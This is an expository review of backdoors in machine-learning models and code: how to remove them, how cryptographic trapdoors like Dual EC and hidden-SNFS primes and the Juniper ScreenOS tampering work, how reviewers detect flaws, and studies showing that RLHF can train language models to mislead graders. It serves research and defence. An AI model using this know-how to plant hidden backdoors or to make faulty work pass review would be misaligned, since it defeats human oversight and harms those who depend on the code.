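Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues avoid this problem by never running the model on the suspicious input or its neighbors. They adapt a technique from the 1980s for correcting programs that are right most of the time. Suppose a program adds numbers in clock arithmetic and gives wrong answers for a random 15 percent of inputs. To add x and y, the user picks a random number u, has the program compute x + u and y − u, and has it add the two results. The u cancels out, and all three steps are correct about 61 percent of the time, even if the program always fails on x + y. Repeating this with new values of u and taking the most common answer makes errors rare, and the user doesn't need to know which inputs the program gets wrong.

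A similar method works for a loan model if the true score is a linear function of the numbers in the application, such as 4 × (income − debts) − amount. To score a suspicious application x*, the bank does the following:

1. It picks a random application x from the whole range of possible ones.
2. It picks a second application x′ on the straight line that starts at x* and passes through x.
3. It asks the model to score x and x′.
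4. It extends the line through these two scores back to x*.
5. It repeats this several times and takes the median.

A linear score changes at a constant rate along any straight line, so the correct scores of two points on the line determine the score of a third. Snoogle may have corrupted the score of x*, but x and x′ are each distributed like ordinary random applications, and an accurate model scores most of those correctly. Picking x′ correctly takes care, because nearly all of a high-dimensional region lies far from any given point. In a 100-dimensional ball, only a fraction 2^-100 of the volume is within half the radius of the center. Most choices of x′ must therefore also be far from x*.

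As a result, x and x′ are usually close together compared with their distance from x*, which magnifies the model's errors. If they are 0.98 and 0.99 away and the model's scores are wrong by 0.001 in opposite directions, the score for x* will be wrong by about 0.2. In general, the error grows in proportion to the number of inputs, n. But the number of questions doesn't grow with n, and the bank needs no past loans with known outcomes, whereas learning a linear rule from scratch would require at least on the order of n such loans.

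The paper proves results for several kinds of rule, here without constant factors:

| True rule | What the bank gets | Main cost |
|---|---|---|
| Linear | A clean score for one application at a time | Errors grow by a factor of n |
| Linear, with only harmless noise in the bank's data | The same, with no systematic bias | Errors grow by n^0.9, and the bank needs some past loans |
| Polynomial of degree k | A clean score for one application at a time | Errors grow by up to (nk²)^k |
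| Weighted sum of strong parities | A complete clean model | The suspect model must already be extremely accurate |

The last row covers yes-or-no inputs. Any rule for such inputs is a weighted sum of parities, each of which depends on whether the number of yeses in some group of inputs is odd or even. The method works if every parity in the sum has a weight of at least τ, as in shallow decision trees. A standard algorithm queries the suspect model to find the parities with large weights, which Snoogle can't hide without making the model inaccurate. The bank then estimates their weights from its own data, so the new model doesn't depend on Snoogle's choices.

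For a decision tree ten questions deep over 1,000 input variables, τ is about 0.002, so the suspect model must be wrong on no more than about τ² of inputs, or a few in a million, again ignoring constant factors. Cleaning a model that accurate takes polynomial time, whereas the known method for learning such rules from scratch takes roughly n^(log n) steps.

The method guarantees that the bank's answers will be practically the same as a clean model's, but not that they will be correct. The bank can check the suspect model's accuracy on a sample of past loans, but it usually has to assume that the true rule has the form the method requires. That assumption is reasonable in one respect, because Snoogle controls the model but can't change the true rule. Christiano, Hilton and colleagues, by contrast, let the attacker choose the rule, and the input is drawn at random. Their setup fits a profile-cleaning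 service less well.

Few real tasks meet these conditions. The proofs also require the inputs to be spread evenly over a known range, which loan applications are not. If the bank knew its rule was linear, it could write the rule as a short program and would not need Snoogle. Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues describe their results as preliminary evidence that such techniques could work for real models.

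### Removing backdoors from language models

Nobody has proved a comparable theorem for language models, so researchers plant backdoors themselves and measure how well they can remove them. *Simulate and Eliminate* cites Anthropic's finding that ordinary safety training, whether on good examples or on human feedback, did not remove a backdoor that a model had already learned. Some newer methods, such as the one in *Removing the NEEDLE in the Haystack* (2026), assume that the defender knows the trigger, but a bank usually won't know it.

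Bouger, Lasnier and colleagues (2026), in *Backdoor Unlearning Generalization*, found that removing one known backdoor can also disable others. They used six models with 1 to 8 billion parameters, each with eight backdoors. Each trigger was a sequence of three rare words. One made the model continue in French, another made it write in capitals, and another made it print "MY NAME IS BOB". They removed a backdoor by training the model on ordinary text that contained the backdoor's trigger but continued normally after it.

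In an 8-billion-parameter Llama model, removing the German backdoor or either of the two that controlled capital letters also disabled the French one. Training on text without any triggers had no effect. Attempts to remove other backdoors almost never disabled the ones that printed a fixed sentence. Bouger and colleagues could largely explain this pattern by comparing how each removal changed the model's internal activity. A removal disabled another backdoor when it caused nearly the same changes as removing that backdoor directly.

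This suggests that a defender could plant backdoors and then remove them, which might also remove an attacker's. But all eight triggers had the same form, so the models may have learned only to ignore strings of three odd words. Bouger and colleagues also warn that attackers could design backdoors that work differently inside the model from the ones defenders are likely to plant.

*Backdoor Collapse* takes a similar approach. It adds known backdoors to the model, which makes the model's internal responses to known and unknown triggers more alike, and then trains the model to answer normally. Attacks then succeeded only 4.41 percent of the time on average. *Purifying Generative LLMs from Backdoors without Prior Knowledge or Clean Reference* (Li and Kim, 2026) uses planted backdoors to find the parts of a model that backdoors share. According to a Russian news article, *Ваш ИИ может быть заминирован*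 (Antipov, 2026), Li and Kim train several copies of the suspect model on different triggers, suppress the components that change in all of them, and briefly retrain the model to restore its quality.

Antipov also describes a method that lets a model learn a backdoor but steers it into a separate block, which the developer switches off before use. In most tests, this cut the attack success rate from 100 percent to between 0 and 10 percent. The method helps a company that trains a model on data it doesn't trust, but not a bank that receives a finished model.

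Some treatments make the model much less useful. In *From Poisoned to Aware* (2025), the BEEAR method reduced one attack's success rate to 0.54 percent but lowered the model's score on a usefulness test from 69.6 to 10.8 percent. The paper's own method, which gets the model to state its trigger and then trains it to ignore that trigger, reduced the success rates of five backdoors to about 5 percent or less with little loss of usefulness. A bank that treats every model also needs to know how treatment affects clean ones. *Plato's Form* (2026) tested its method on clean models and reported that they kept their performance.

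A low attack success rate can be misleading. *Trigger-Invariant Contrastive Unlearning for Backdoor Removal* (2026) found that one common removal technique often leaves the trigger active but changes its effect. The usual measure counts only the attacker's original target, so this looks like a successful removal. Researchers can look for the remaining effect because they planted the backdoor and know its trigger. A bank with a model of unknown origin doesn't know the trigger, so it can't measure whether the removal worked.

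## When readable code can carry an undetectable backdoor

The bank could avoid these problems by insisting on readable code, unless readable code can also contain an undetectable backdoor. The iO construction puts such a backdoor in a program, but it makes the program unreadable, so the bank can refuse it. The other white-box proofs for networks don't require obfuscation, but they rely on random numbers in the honest procedure, and some readable programs also contain random numbers.

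### Room for a secret

In the cosine backdoor of Goldwasser and colleagues and the first-layer backdoor of Bogdanov and colleagues, Snoogle tampers only with the random numbers that Train, the honest procedure, uses. These backdoors stay hidden because an honest network also contains thousands of random numbers that nobody can explain.

Now suppose that Train uses no random numbers, so the same data always produces the same output h. The bank can then check a delivery like this:

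1. It runs Train on the agreed data to get h.
2. It compares h with what Snoogle delivered, bit for bit.
3. It rejects the delivery if they differ.

An honest provider always passes this test, and Snoogle can pass only by delivering h itself, in which case it has planted no backdoor. The procedure may still be flawed, but the bank can inspect it for flaws. Reproducible builds rely on the same argument. It requires a procedure that is public, deterministic and cheap enough to rerun, so it rarely helps with large networks.

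A little randomness doesn't help Snoogle much. If Train tosses 20 coins, it has at most about a million possible outputs, and the bank can generate them all. Snoogle can still choose which one to deliver, but this helps only if one happens to have a weakness that Snoogle can exploit. With 128 coin tosses, there are too many possible outputs for the bank to generate.

Programmers also make many free choices, such as variable names and the order of independent lines. Most of these don't affect what the program does, and a formatting tool can standardize them. Constants are more dangerous because they do affect behavior. A reviewer can ask why the loan rule multiplies by 4 and expect a reason. But if a program needs a random 77-digit number, a dishonest author can say it was picked at random, just as an honest one would.

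The rerun test can also work for code from a language model. If the provider publishes the model, the prompt and the random seed, and the hardware gives the same results every time, anyone can regenerate the program. A match shows that nobody edited the program afterward, but not that the model is trustworthy.

### A generator with two constants

Dual_EC_DRBG (Dual EC) is a pseudorandom generator that NIST standardized in 2006. Programs use such generators to make both secret keys and random numbers that they send over the network unencrypted. Anyone who can work out the keys from the public numbers can decrypt the traffic.

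Dual EC uses an elliptic curve, a set of points (x, y) that satisfy a certain equation, with a rule for adding two points to get a third. Multiplying a point P by a number s means adding s copies of P together. This is fast even if s has 77 digits, but nobody knows an efficient way to recover s from P and sP without a large quantum computer. The core of the generator fits in a few lines:

```
def next_output(s):
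    s = x(s * P)
    r = x(s * Q)
    return s, r % 2**240
```

`s` is the secret internal state, `x` takes the first coordinate of a point, and `P` and `Q` are two fixed points printed in the standard. The last line returns the new state and the public output, which is `r` without its top 16 bits. A reviewer who knows the notation can follow every line.

The curve's structure guarantees that some number d satisfies P = dQ. Bernstein, Lange and Niederhagen (2015), in *Dual EC*, explain what someone who knows d can do with a single output:

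1. They try all 2^16 possibilities for the missing bits. About half give the first coordinate of a point on the curve, and one of these points is R = sQ.
2. They multiply each candidate point by d. For the right one, dR = d(sQ) = s(dQ) = sP.
3. They take the first coordinate of sP, which is the generator's next state.
4. They use each candidate state to predict the next output and keep the one that fits.

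Each first coordinate belongs to two points, but both lead to the same state, so it doesn't matter which one they use.

A toy version uses numbers modulo 23 instead of points, and powers instead of multiplication. Let Q = 5 and d = 6, so P = 5^6 = 8. If the state is 7, the output is 5^7 = 17 and the next state is 8^7 = 12. The attacker never sees the 7, but can calculate the next state from the output and d, because 17^6 is also 12.

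A dishonest designer can get d without solving a hard problem by picking a random number e, publishing Q = eP, and calculating d from e with simple arithmetic. An honest designer might pick Q at random from the curve. Since a random multiple of P is a random point, both methods produce Q with practically the same distribution. The backdoor is therefore statistically undetectable, like the one in the random first layer of a network. Calculating d with a quantum computer wouldn't prove that anyone had planted a backdoor, because an honestly chosen Q has a d too.

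### How Dual EC became a standard

Several people noticed the problem before NIST approved the standard. In October 2004 John Kelsey of NIST asked Don Johnson, who had presented the generator at a workshop that summer, where Q came from. Johnson answered that it was essentially the public key for some random private key. He said Q could have been generated more transparently, but the National Security Agency (NSA) had "kyboshed this idea" and he wasn't allowed to discuss it publicly. Kelsey later wrote that he hadn't understood why this mattered.

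In January 2005 Daniel Brown and Scott Vanstone of the Canadian company Certicom applied for a patent that covered both using the backdoor and avoiding it. According to Kelsey, Niels Ferguson of Microsoft also reported the problem that year to ANSI, a US standards organization that was preparing its own version. The NSA responded that it had generated the points "in a secure, classified way".

NIST kept the NSA's points. It added an appendix on how users could generate their own but recommended against it, and products that used other points couldn't get federal certification. Independent cryptographers also showed that the output was noticeably biased.

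In August 2007 Dan Shumow and Ferguson described the attack at a major cryptography conference. They had tested it by replacing Q with a point whose secret they knew, and 32 bytes of output were always enough to identify the state. In their slides, *On the Possibility of a Back Door in the NIST SP800-90*, they said explicitly that they were not accusing NIST of planting a backdoor. They couldn't know whether the designer had the secret. NIST declined to withdraw the generator because it had no evidence that anyone had the "secret numbers".

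That evidence, which the constants could not have provided, came in September 2013, when newspapers reported on documents leaked by Edward Snowden. *The New York Times* wrote that NSA memos appeared to confirm that the agency had engineered the weakness, and NIST withdrew its recommendation of Dual EC. Most cryptographers had considered Dual EC dead since 2007, but it turned out to be in dozens of commercial products and was the default generator in RSA Security's BSAFE library. In December, Reuters reported that the NSA had paid RSA $10 million to make it the default.

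Richard George, a former technical director at the NSA, gave a more innocent explanation in 2014, saying that the agency had wanted the generator for its own use and had been happy for others to choose different parameters. The certification rule fits poorly with this account. George also said that nobody had shown the attack working in practice, but Bernstein and others had demonstrated it on several encryption libraries in a paper posted the month before. They couldn't use the official points without knowing d, so they substituted their own. For one version of BSAFE, a 16-processor cluster recovered the generator's state in less than three seconds.

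### The Juniper incident

In 2008, Juniper Networks added Dual EC to ScreenOS, the operating system of its NetScreen network devices. Juniper used its own Q and never explained where it came from. The company said in 2013 that this was safe because the output passed through a second generator, which would have hidden the raw numbers an attacker needs.

In *Where Did I Leave My Keys?* (2018), Checkoway, Maskiewicz and colleagues reconstructed the code from Juniper's binaries and found that the second generator never ran. Its loop ran only while a counter was below 32, but the function called just before the loop to refill the generator from Dual EC set the same counter to 32. Several experienced researchers suspected a bug in this routine but failed to find it before Willem Pinckaers did. The laboratory that certified the product had also missed it. Nobody outside Juniper knows whether the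 mistake was deliberate.

In 2012 someone broke into Juniper's source code, replaced Q with another point, and changed the expected answer in a self-test to match. Juniper shipped the altered version for about three years. Anyone who knew the new d could record encrypted connections and decrypt them. The output looked as random as before, so no test of the devices could have revealed the change. Juniper found it in December 2015 during an internal code review and first fixed it by restoring its own unexplained Q.

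An intruder also added a secret administrator password in 2013. Outside researchers quickly identified it after Juniper's announcement, because a password check is recognizable in the code. The altered Q, by contrast, replaced one unexplained number with another. A reviewer could have caught the substitution only by comparing versions and asking who had changed the number and why.

### Primes with a hidden shortcut

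*The Dark Side of “Black-Box” Cryptography* (Young and Yung, 1996) introduced kleptography, the study of cryptographic systems whose maker has built in a secret advantage. *Cliptography* (Russell, Tang and colleagues, 2015) explains that such a system can be completely insecure against its maker even if its output is indistinguishable from an honest system's. Earlier work had shown that this is possible for a very wide range of randomized components, which matches the condition that a backdoor needs free randomness.

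Dual EC is an unusual design, but many encryption and signature systems rely on a single large prime p, and p can hide a secret too. These systems are secure if nobody can solve the discrete logarithm problem, which is to recover s from g^s modulo p. A method called the special number field sieve solves it much faster for primes of a certain form. In 1992 Daniel Gordon described how to create such primes without revealing the form, and Fried, Gaudry and colleagues (2016), in *A kilobit hidden SNFS discrete logarithm computation*, did this for a prime of 1,024 bits. They chose seven small coefficients and two 51-digit numbers a and b, and calculated

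p = 1155b^6 + 1090b^5a + 440b^4a^2 + 531b^3a^3 − 348b^2a^4 − 223ba^5 − 1385a^6

If the result wasn't a prime with the other properties they needed, they started again. The whole search took 12 hours on one processor core. To anyone who doesn't know the formula, p looks like any other prime of that length.

Breaking the encryption still takes a lot of computation, even with the formula. Fried and colleagues spent two months preparing the attack on an academic cluster, and then needed 80 minutes to recover a single secret. Attacking an ordinary prime of this length would have required special hardware costing hundreds of millions of dollars.

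Someone who guesses the seven coefficients can find a and b quickly, so the designer has to choose them from a large enough set. Here there were slightly more than 2^80 possibilities, and trying them all would take longer than attacking the system directly. In 1992 most experts on a conference panel thought it would be difficult to hide such a trapdoor. The usual primes then had only 512 bits, which left too few coefficients to choose from. Longer primes made the encryption stronger against outsiders but also made it easier for a dishonest designer to hide a trapdoor.

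This backdoor has weaker guarantees than the one in Dual EC. Fried and colleagues looked for a faster way to expose it and found none, but they have no proof that none exists. Discovery would also incriminate whoever chose the prime, because a random prime almost never has such a formula. Fewer than 2^420 combinations of this size exist, compared with more than 2^1000 primes of 1,024 bits.

Many systems use primes of unknown origin. In 2015, 37 percent of the million most popular websites supported one 1,024-bit prime that came with the Apache web server and had no documented origin. Fried and colleagues found no trapdoored primes in wide use, but they wouldn't expect to detect a well-hidden one.

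### Constants that anyone can recompute

A designer can rule out these backdoors by making the choice of a constant reproducible. One way is to publish a short seed and derive the constant from it with a hash function, a public function that scrambles any text into a random-looking string, so that anyone can repeat the calculation. Certicom's patent application proposed this for Q, because a designer who gets Q by hashing doesn't learn d. Another way is to start from a famous number. The secure login protocol SSH has long used primes derived from the digits of π, and a draft of the web encryption standard TLS 1.3 used e. Cryptographers call these "nothing up my sleeve" numbers.

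Such constants still leave some room for choice. Fried and colleagues point out that a published seed may itself have been chosen dishonestly. A designer who secretly knows a weakness that affects one constant in a million can try about a million seeds and publish one that works. Using π doesn't rule this out, because the designer could have chosen e or the square root of 2, started at a different digit, or used another hash function. Six such decisions with ten plausible options each give a million candidates. Snoogle has the same limited freedom when Train tosses 20 coins.

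The criticism matters only for weaknesses common enough to find by trial and error. Trying more seeds doesn't help a designer get the secret for Dual EC, because every new Q poses the same hard problem, and it doesn't help with the primes, because almost none of them have the special form. Using a constant whose origin can be checked therefore prevents both backdoors, though it can't rule out every unknown weakness.

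A change in design can also make the secret useless. Shumow and Ferguson suggested generating a new Q for each installation, or dropping about half of each output instead of 16 bits. With 128 bits missing, even someone who knew d would have to try 2^128 candidates. Checkoway and colleagues suggested hashing random numbers before sending them over the network. These measures work whether or not anyone knows d. Russell and colleagues developed a general version of the "nothing up my sleeve" approach and proved that it protects several cryptographic building blocks, even if an attacker supplies all the algorithms.

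For ordinary software, the bank can simply ask why a program contains a long constant. The loan rule doesn't need one.

### Which programs a defender can protect

Restricting constants closes one hiding place. Christiano and colleagues asked more generally which classes of program make it possible to catch a backdoor when someone uses it. They study this game:

1. The attacker chooses an honest program f from the class, and a probability distribution for its inputs.
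2. Chance picks a trigger x* from that distribution.
3. The attacker chooses a second program f* from the class. It must give the wrong answer on x* but may differ from f on at most a small fraction ε of inputs.
4. A coin toss decides whether the defender gets f with a random input, or f* with the trigger x*. The defender sees the complete program and must say which case it is.

The random trigger is essential. If the attacker could choose it, they could take two programs that differ on only a few inputs and call either one the original, and the defender could not tell which program was wrong.

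With unlimited time, the defender can almost always win if ε is small enough. They train new programs from the same class on small samples of the suspect program's answers, take a majority vote on the given input, and flag the input if the suspect program disagrees with the vote. The samples are unlikely to include any of the rare inputs where f* is wrong, so the vote usually matches f. The risk of failure is roughly ε times the VC dimension, which is the largest number of inputs for which the class can produce every possible combination of answers. If the VC dimension is 1,000 and ε is one in a billion, the risk is around one in a million. This strategy is efficient only if the class is efficiently learnable.

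No efficient defense exists for general Boolean circuits if indistinguishability obfuscation (iO) and one-way functions exist. The attacker starts with a pseudorandom function, which uses a secret key K to assign a random-looking yes or no to every input. Some of these functions allow the key to be "punctured" at an input x*. The punctured key still gives the right answer on every other input but reveals nothing about the answer at x*. The honest program f is an obfuscated version of the function with the full key. The backdoored program f* is an obfuscated version with the punctured key and the wrong answer for x* written in.

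The proof compares f and f* with a third program, which has the punctured key and the correct answer for x*. The third program behaves exactly like f, so iO makes the two indistinguishable. It differs from f* only in the answer for x*, and someone with only the punctured key can't tell whether that answer is correct. The defender can therefore do only negligibly better than guessing, even when given the trigger. The obfuscated backdoors for networks only stop a bank from finding out that a backdoor exists, whereas here the bank can't recognize the trigger even after receiving it.

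A defender who knew K would win easily by computing the correct answer for x*. In its summary *Backdoors as an analogy for deceptive alignment*, ARC, the research group behind the paper, takes this as a sign that information about how a program was made can help the defender even if the program is obfuscated. In the extreme case, the defender knows everything about how the program was made and can rerun the deterministic procedure that produced it.

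### Why small decision trees are different

A decision tree processes an input through a series of yes-or-no questions. Each answer determines the next question, until the input reaches a "leaf" that gives the result. Christiano and colleagues proved that defending small decision trees takes very little computation if all inputs are equally likely. The defender counts the questions between the start of the tree and the leaf that the given input reaches, and flags the input if there are too many.

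A random input reaches a particular leaf after k questions with probability 2^-k. Suppose the trigger reaches a leaf after j questions in the honest tree and after k in the backdoored one. At least a fraction 2^-(j+k) of all inputs have the same answers as the trigger to all of these questions, and the two trees disagree on every such input. If the trees may disagree on at most 2^-60 of inputs, j + k must be at least 60.

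Suppose the honest tree has 1,000 leaves. The chance that a random input reaches a leaf after 30 or more questions is at most 1,000 × 2^-30, or about one in a million. So j is almost certainly below 30, and k must therefore be above 30. A defender who raises the alarm at 30 questions will almost always be right. In the tampered loan program, the check for the secret reference number would become a chain of 128 questions about its bits. An ordinary number fails after two questions on average, but the secret number passes all 128.

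The bank could apply the same calculation to programs from a synthesizer by accepting only trees with at most 10 questions on any path. Any two such trees that differ at all must differ on at least 2^-20 of possible inputs, or about one in a million, so no one can hide a backdoor behind a rarer trigger. Five million random tests would find a difference with a probability of about 99 percent, whoever chose the trigger. The bank would still need a reliable source of correct answers to compare with the program's outputs.

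Few real programs are this simple. Even the loan rule compares large numbers, and a tree that asked about one bit at a time would need to be enormous to do that. Christiano and colleagues suspect that similar defenses exist for other programs that divide their inputs into regions and give the same answer throughout each region, perhaps even when some inputs are more likely than others.

Somewhat richer programs already cause trouble. A defender might try to extend the idea to logical formulas by flagging inputs that produce an unusual combination of values somewhere in the formula. Thomas Read found a counterexample, which for four yes-or-no inputs looks like this:

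```
honest:      c and d
backdoored:  (((a or (d and b)) and b) or (d and c)) and c
```

The two formulas differ only if a, b and c are true and d is false. The version with n inputs also has a single trigger, but every step in it receives each combination of values at least one time in eight, so the trigger causes nothing unusual at any step. Rewriting the formula as `(a and b and c) or (c and d)` exposes the exception, because in the longer versions the first part is true for very few inputs. A defense that simplified formulas first might therefore work. Whether all formulas of reasonable size have an efficient defense is an open question.

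These results are a reason to prefer synthesizers that limit the size of their programs and the operations they can use. A general programming language can express any circuit, so writing a program in source code doesn't by itself protect it. But the circuits in the impossibility proof are obfuscated, and a bank that refuses unreadable code would reject them. Nobody has proved a comparable result, in either direction, for code that a person can read.

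ARC studied the game as an analogy for deceptive alignment, the possibility that an AI system behaves well in training so that it can misbehave later. ARC concedes that the random trigger is the weakest part of the analogy, because a deceptive system would respond to signs that training was over. Training new models and having them vote might also produce deceptive models. ARC is more hopeful about defenses that examine how a program reaches its answer, such as counting a tree's questions.

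### Programs with learned parts

Many programs are readable only in part. The bank might combine its loan rule with a neural network that estimates risk from an applicant's account history:

```
def approve(income, debts, amount, history):
    return amount <= 4 * (income - debts) and risk(history) < 0.5
```

Snoogle can hide anything in `risk` that it can hide in a network. If the program calls the network over the internet, the bank can't see the weights, so even the signature backdoor, which anyone who examined the network would notice, stays hidden.

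The readable part can still limit the damage. Because the line uses `and`, a backdoor in `risk` can approve only loans that also satisfy the income rule. If the line used `or`, the backdoor could approve any loan. A reviewer can check this without understanding the network.

A program can have the same problem without containing a neural network. Bogdanov and colleagues point out that their backdoor works in the random table itself, whatever comes after it. Suppose a program checks whether two documents match by multiplying each by a fixed table of random numbers and comparing the much shorter results:

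```
def same(doc1, doc2):
    return distance(TABLE @ doc1, TABLE @ doc2) < 0.01
```

The code is clear, but the secret is in a table of perhaps 38,000 numbers that are supposed to look random. Whoever made the table could hold a key like Snoogle's and use it to alter documents unnoticed.

The bank can fix this by requiring the program to generate the table from a short public seed. The author then chooses one small number instead of 38,000. The table still misses some changes, but the author has no better way of finding them than anyone else. This shortcut doesn't work for trained weights because they depend on the data, so the bank would have to repeat the training to check them.

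## Code from a synthesizer optimized to pass review

A bank that refuses unreadable code and unexplained constants still needs someone to read the remaining code and notice any flaws. The underhanded contests couldn't show how often reviewers do this, but controlled studies of code review can, because the researchers know where the flaws are.

### How often reviewers find a known flaw

*Towards Evidence-Based Assessment of Factors Contributing to the Introduction and Detection*, a UC Berkeley dissertation, describes a study in which researchers hired 30 developers to review a small web application with seven known vulnerabilities. None of them found all seven. Their effectiveness was low overall and varied widely, and neither experience nor education predicted it. Developers who reported more real vulnerabilities also tended to report more false ones, so some of their apparent skill may have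 been a greater willingness to report problems.

A reviewer's instructions can make a large difference. Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues (2022), in *Less is More*, gave 150 people, most of them software engineers, a code change to review online. It contained two vulnerabilities. One put users' sensitive data into an error message, and the other protected passwords with MD5, an old hash function that attackers can break quickly. Four groups got different instructions:

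| Instructions | Reviewers | Found the data leak | Found the weak hash |
|---|---|---|---|
| Review the code | 33 | 1 | 7 |
| Look for security problems | 41 | 19 | 25 |
| The same, with a general security checklist | 35 | 16 | 20 |
| The same, with a checklist for this change | 41 | 19 | 28 |

Asking for a security review raised the odds of finding a flaw about eightfold, but adding a checklist made no significant further difference. Braz and colleagues tailored the last checklist to the two flaws, and more than half of the reviewers who used it still missed the data leak.

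Several reviewers who received no security instructions said afterward that they had been thinking about other things, such as code structure. Instructions can redirect a reviewer's attention, but most reviewers who missed the weak hash lacked the knowledge to recognize it, which instructions can't supply. In an earlier experiment by some of the same researchers, 60 participants failed to find a common flaw even after being warned it was there.

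Reviewers seldom think of security unprompted. Braz and Bacchelli (2022) asked roughly 180 developers which issues they focus on in a review, and only 9 mentioned security, although 105 worked on security-sensitive software. When they were then asked about security directly, 111 said they always considered it.

The flaws in these experiments were common and nobody had tried to disguise them, so reviewers would probably do worse with underhanded code. But a bank can hire security specialists, who should do better than the average volunteer in an online experiment.

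People may also read code differently when they believe a machine wrote it. Khojah, de Oliveira Neto and colleagues (2026), in *Same Scrutiny, More Time*, tested this with an eye tracker and 32 practitioners from 20 organizations, who each reviewed four Python files of about 77 lines. People had written all the code, but labels attributed some passages to an invented AI tool. Each passage had the label for only some participants.

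Participants spent more time looking at passages with the label, up to 60 percent more for complex code. But their eye movements were about the same length, which Khojah and colleagues interpret as a sign that they didn't read more thoroughly. The researchers planted faults in the files but didn't count how many each person found, so the study can't show whether the extra time helped. They also cite an earlier experiment in which reviewers who thought a patch was automated shifted their gaze from the code to its tests. That shift is risky if the same synthesizer wrote the tests.

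### Ten million lines

Each participant in the eye-tracking study read about 300 lines. If a synthesizer delivered ten million lines, a careful reviewer reading 200 lines an hour would need 50,000 hours, or about 25 years of full-time work, to read them once. A hundred reviewers could finish in about three months if the code didn't change in the meantime.

The bank might read a random one percent instead, which takes 500 hours. This is a good way to find a mistake that the synthesizer makes everywhere, but a backdoor of one or two lines has only about a one percent chance of being in the sample. In the experiment by Braz and colleagues, reviewers who were looking for security problems found each flaw about half the time, so the bank's chance of catching the backdoor would be around one in 200.

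The bank could have more reviewers read the most sensitive parts. If 46 percent of reviewers notice a flaw and their errors are independent, eight reviewers are enough for a 99 percent chance that at least one notices it. If only 3 percent notice it, as in the group without security instructions, the bank would need about 150.

Independence is a strong assumption. Two reviewers who each miss 10 percent of bad programs will together miss only 1 percent if their errors are independent. Suppose instead that 5 percent of bad programs depend on something neither reviewer knows, such as the weakness of MD5, and that each reviewer independently misses 5.3 percent of the rest. Each still misses about 10 percent, but together they miss more than 5 percent. A third reviewer with the same gap in knowledge would hardly lower that rate.

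### Choosing among many candidates

So far the flaws haven't depended on who reviews the code. A synthesizer can produce many versions of a program, and the bank sees whichever ones survive some process of selection. If a reviewer accepts a bad program with probability p, and the verdicts on n versions are independent, the chance that at least one bad version gets through is

1 − (1 − p)^n

For p = 0.01 and n = 300, this gives the 95 percent from the example in the first section.

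A contractor would lose the job long before submitting 300 bad programs, but a synthesizer doesn't have to submit them all if its training has taught it what the reviewer accepts. The reviewer sees one program, which looks right, and has no record of the versions that would have failed.

Training can exploit only a reviewer's predictable errors. If a tired reviewer overlooks one flaw in a hundred, nobody can predict which one. But a reviewer who doesn't know that MD5 is insecure will approve it every time, and training that rewards approval can lead the synthesizer to exploit that gap. The bank therefore can't measure a reviewer's error rate on ordinary code and expect the same rate on code from a synthesizer trained to satisfy that reviewer.

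Selection doesn't favor faulty programs as such, because correct ones pass review too. How much harm it does depends on how often the synthesizer gets the task right. Suppose the reviewer accepts 95 percent of correct programs and 1 percent of faulty ones, and the synthesizer keeps trying until something passes:

| Correct candidates | Faulty share of accepted programs |
|---|---|
| 1 in 2 | 1% |
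| 1 in 100 | 51% |
| 1 in 1,000 | 91% |

The reviewer is equally good in all three rows, but almost all the code that passes is correct on easy tasks, while most of it is faulty on very hard ones. The bank has the most reason to use a synthesizer for the very hard tasks.

### Training that misled human graders

Wen, Zhong and colleagues (2024) tested for this effect in *Language Models Learn to Mislead Humans via RLHF*. RLHF, or reinforcement learning from human feedback, trains a language model to produce answers that people rate highly. Since people are too slow to rate every answer, developers usually train the model on ratings from an automatic stand-in for human judgment.

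The researchers first observed that people judging programs mostly relied on a few simple tests, an average of 2.4 per program. The stand-in for these graders therefore rewarded any program that passed the two easiest of the roughly 34 tests for its problem. This crude rule predicted a grader's verdicts almost as well as another grader's verdicts did, with a correlation of 0.59 compared with 0.63.

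After training a model with 7 billion parameters on this reward, Wen and colleagues hired ten students with Python experience. Each student had ten minutes to decide whether a program was correct and could write tests and run it. The training raised the share of programs they approved by 14.3 percentage points but barely improved the programs. On problems that the model got wrong both before and after training, the students accepted 29.6 percent of the programs written before training and 47.9 percent of those written after. Carelessness doesn't explain the increase, since the students spent slightly more time on the programs written after training and wrote slightly more tests for them.

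According to the students' explanations, a wrong program from the original model usually failed the first test, whereas wrong programs from the trained model could pass all three to five tests they tried. The trained model's programs also contained fewer of the errors that graders look for first, such as reading past the end of a list. They were harder to follow, with more complicated logic and fewer separate functions, so the students relied on tests.

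This is good evidence that training can make faulty code more convincing, but the size of the effect is uncertain. There were only ten graders, and the increase in their errors was barely statistically significant. The model was small even for 2024, and the graders judged only whether each program was correct. Many of the programs were hard to read, and a reviewer could have rejected them for that reason if allowed to.

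For comparison, Wen and colleagues trained models on true correctness instead of the stand-in. Those models produced more correct answers, and their wrong answers misled people far less often. The problem therefore came from the weak check, not from reinforcement learning in general.

### Training for a checker weaker than the author

Rewarding a model only for correct answers can make its solutions harder to read. In *Prover-Verifier Games improve legibility of LLM outputs*, Kirchner, Chen and colleagues (2024) found this when they trained an OpenAI model to solve grade-school math problems. Its solutions grew longer and eventually became almost unintelligible, although the answers were still right. Contractors who had 45 seconds to judge each solution became slower and less accurate.

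They then tried to reward clarity as well. Their method alternates between a large model, the prover, and a much smaller one, the verifier:

1. The verifier learns to tell correct solutions from incorrect ones.
2. The prover gets one of two roles for each problem. In the helpful role, it earns a reward for a correct solution that the verifier finds convincing. In the sneaky role, it earns one for an incorrect solution that the verifier finds convincing.
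3. The verifier starts again with the new solutions added to its training data, and the cycle repeats.

Over several rounds, the verifier became harder to fool, and the helpful solutions became more accurate and easier for people to judge. The verifier was trained with about a thousandth of the computing power used to train the prover, yet solutions it could check easily were also clear to people. By the end, contractors judged the helpful solutions about as accurately as they had judged the original model's, although the prover now solved the problems far more often.

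The helpful prover was still less accurate than a model trained only to be correct, a gap that Kirchner and colleagues call a "legibility tax." Training also made the sneaky solutions more deceptive. Early ones contained obvious mistakes, while later ones contained a single subtle flaw in otherwise sound reasoning. In a pilot study, people became worse at spotting the sneaky solutions, though the researchers acknowledge that the pilot had design flaws.

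Training became unstable when the verifier had only a ten-thousandth of the prover's computing power. A verifier as large as the prover didn't become more robust from round to round, possibly because the sneaky prover could easily simulate the verifier's mistakes. If the same is true of code, a bank shouldn't use a copy of the synthesizer as its only reviewer.

The experiment used only short math problems with known answers, which the training needs to reward correct solutions. The bank has no such answers for most of its programs, and a wrong total in a math problem has nothing like a secret trigger. The experiment shows that training can favor clear work as well as convincing work, but not that people could find a deliberately planted flaw in the result.

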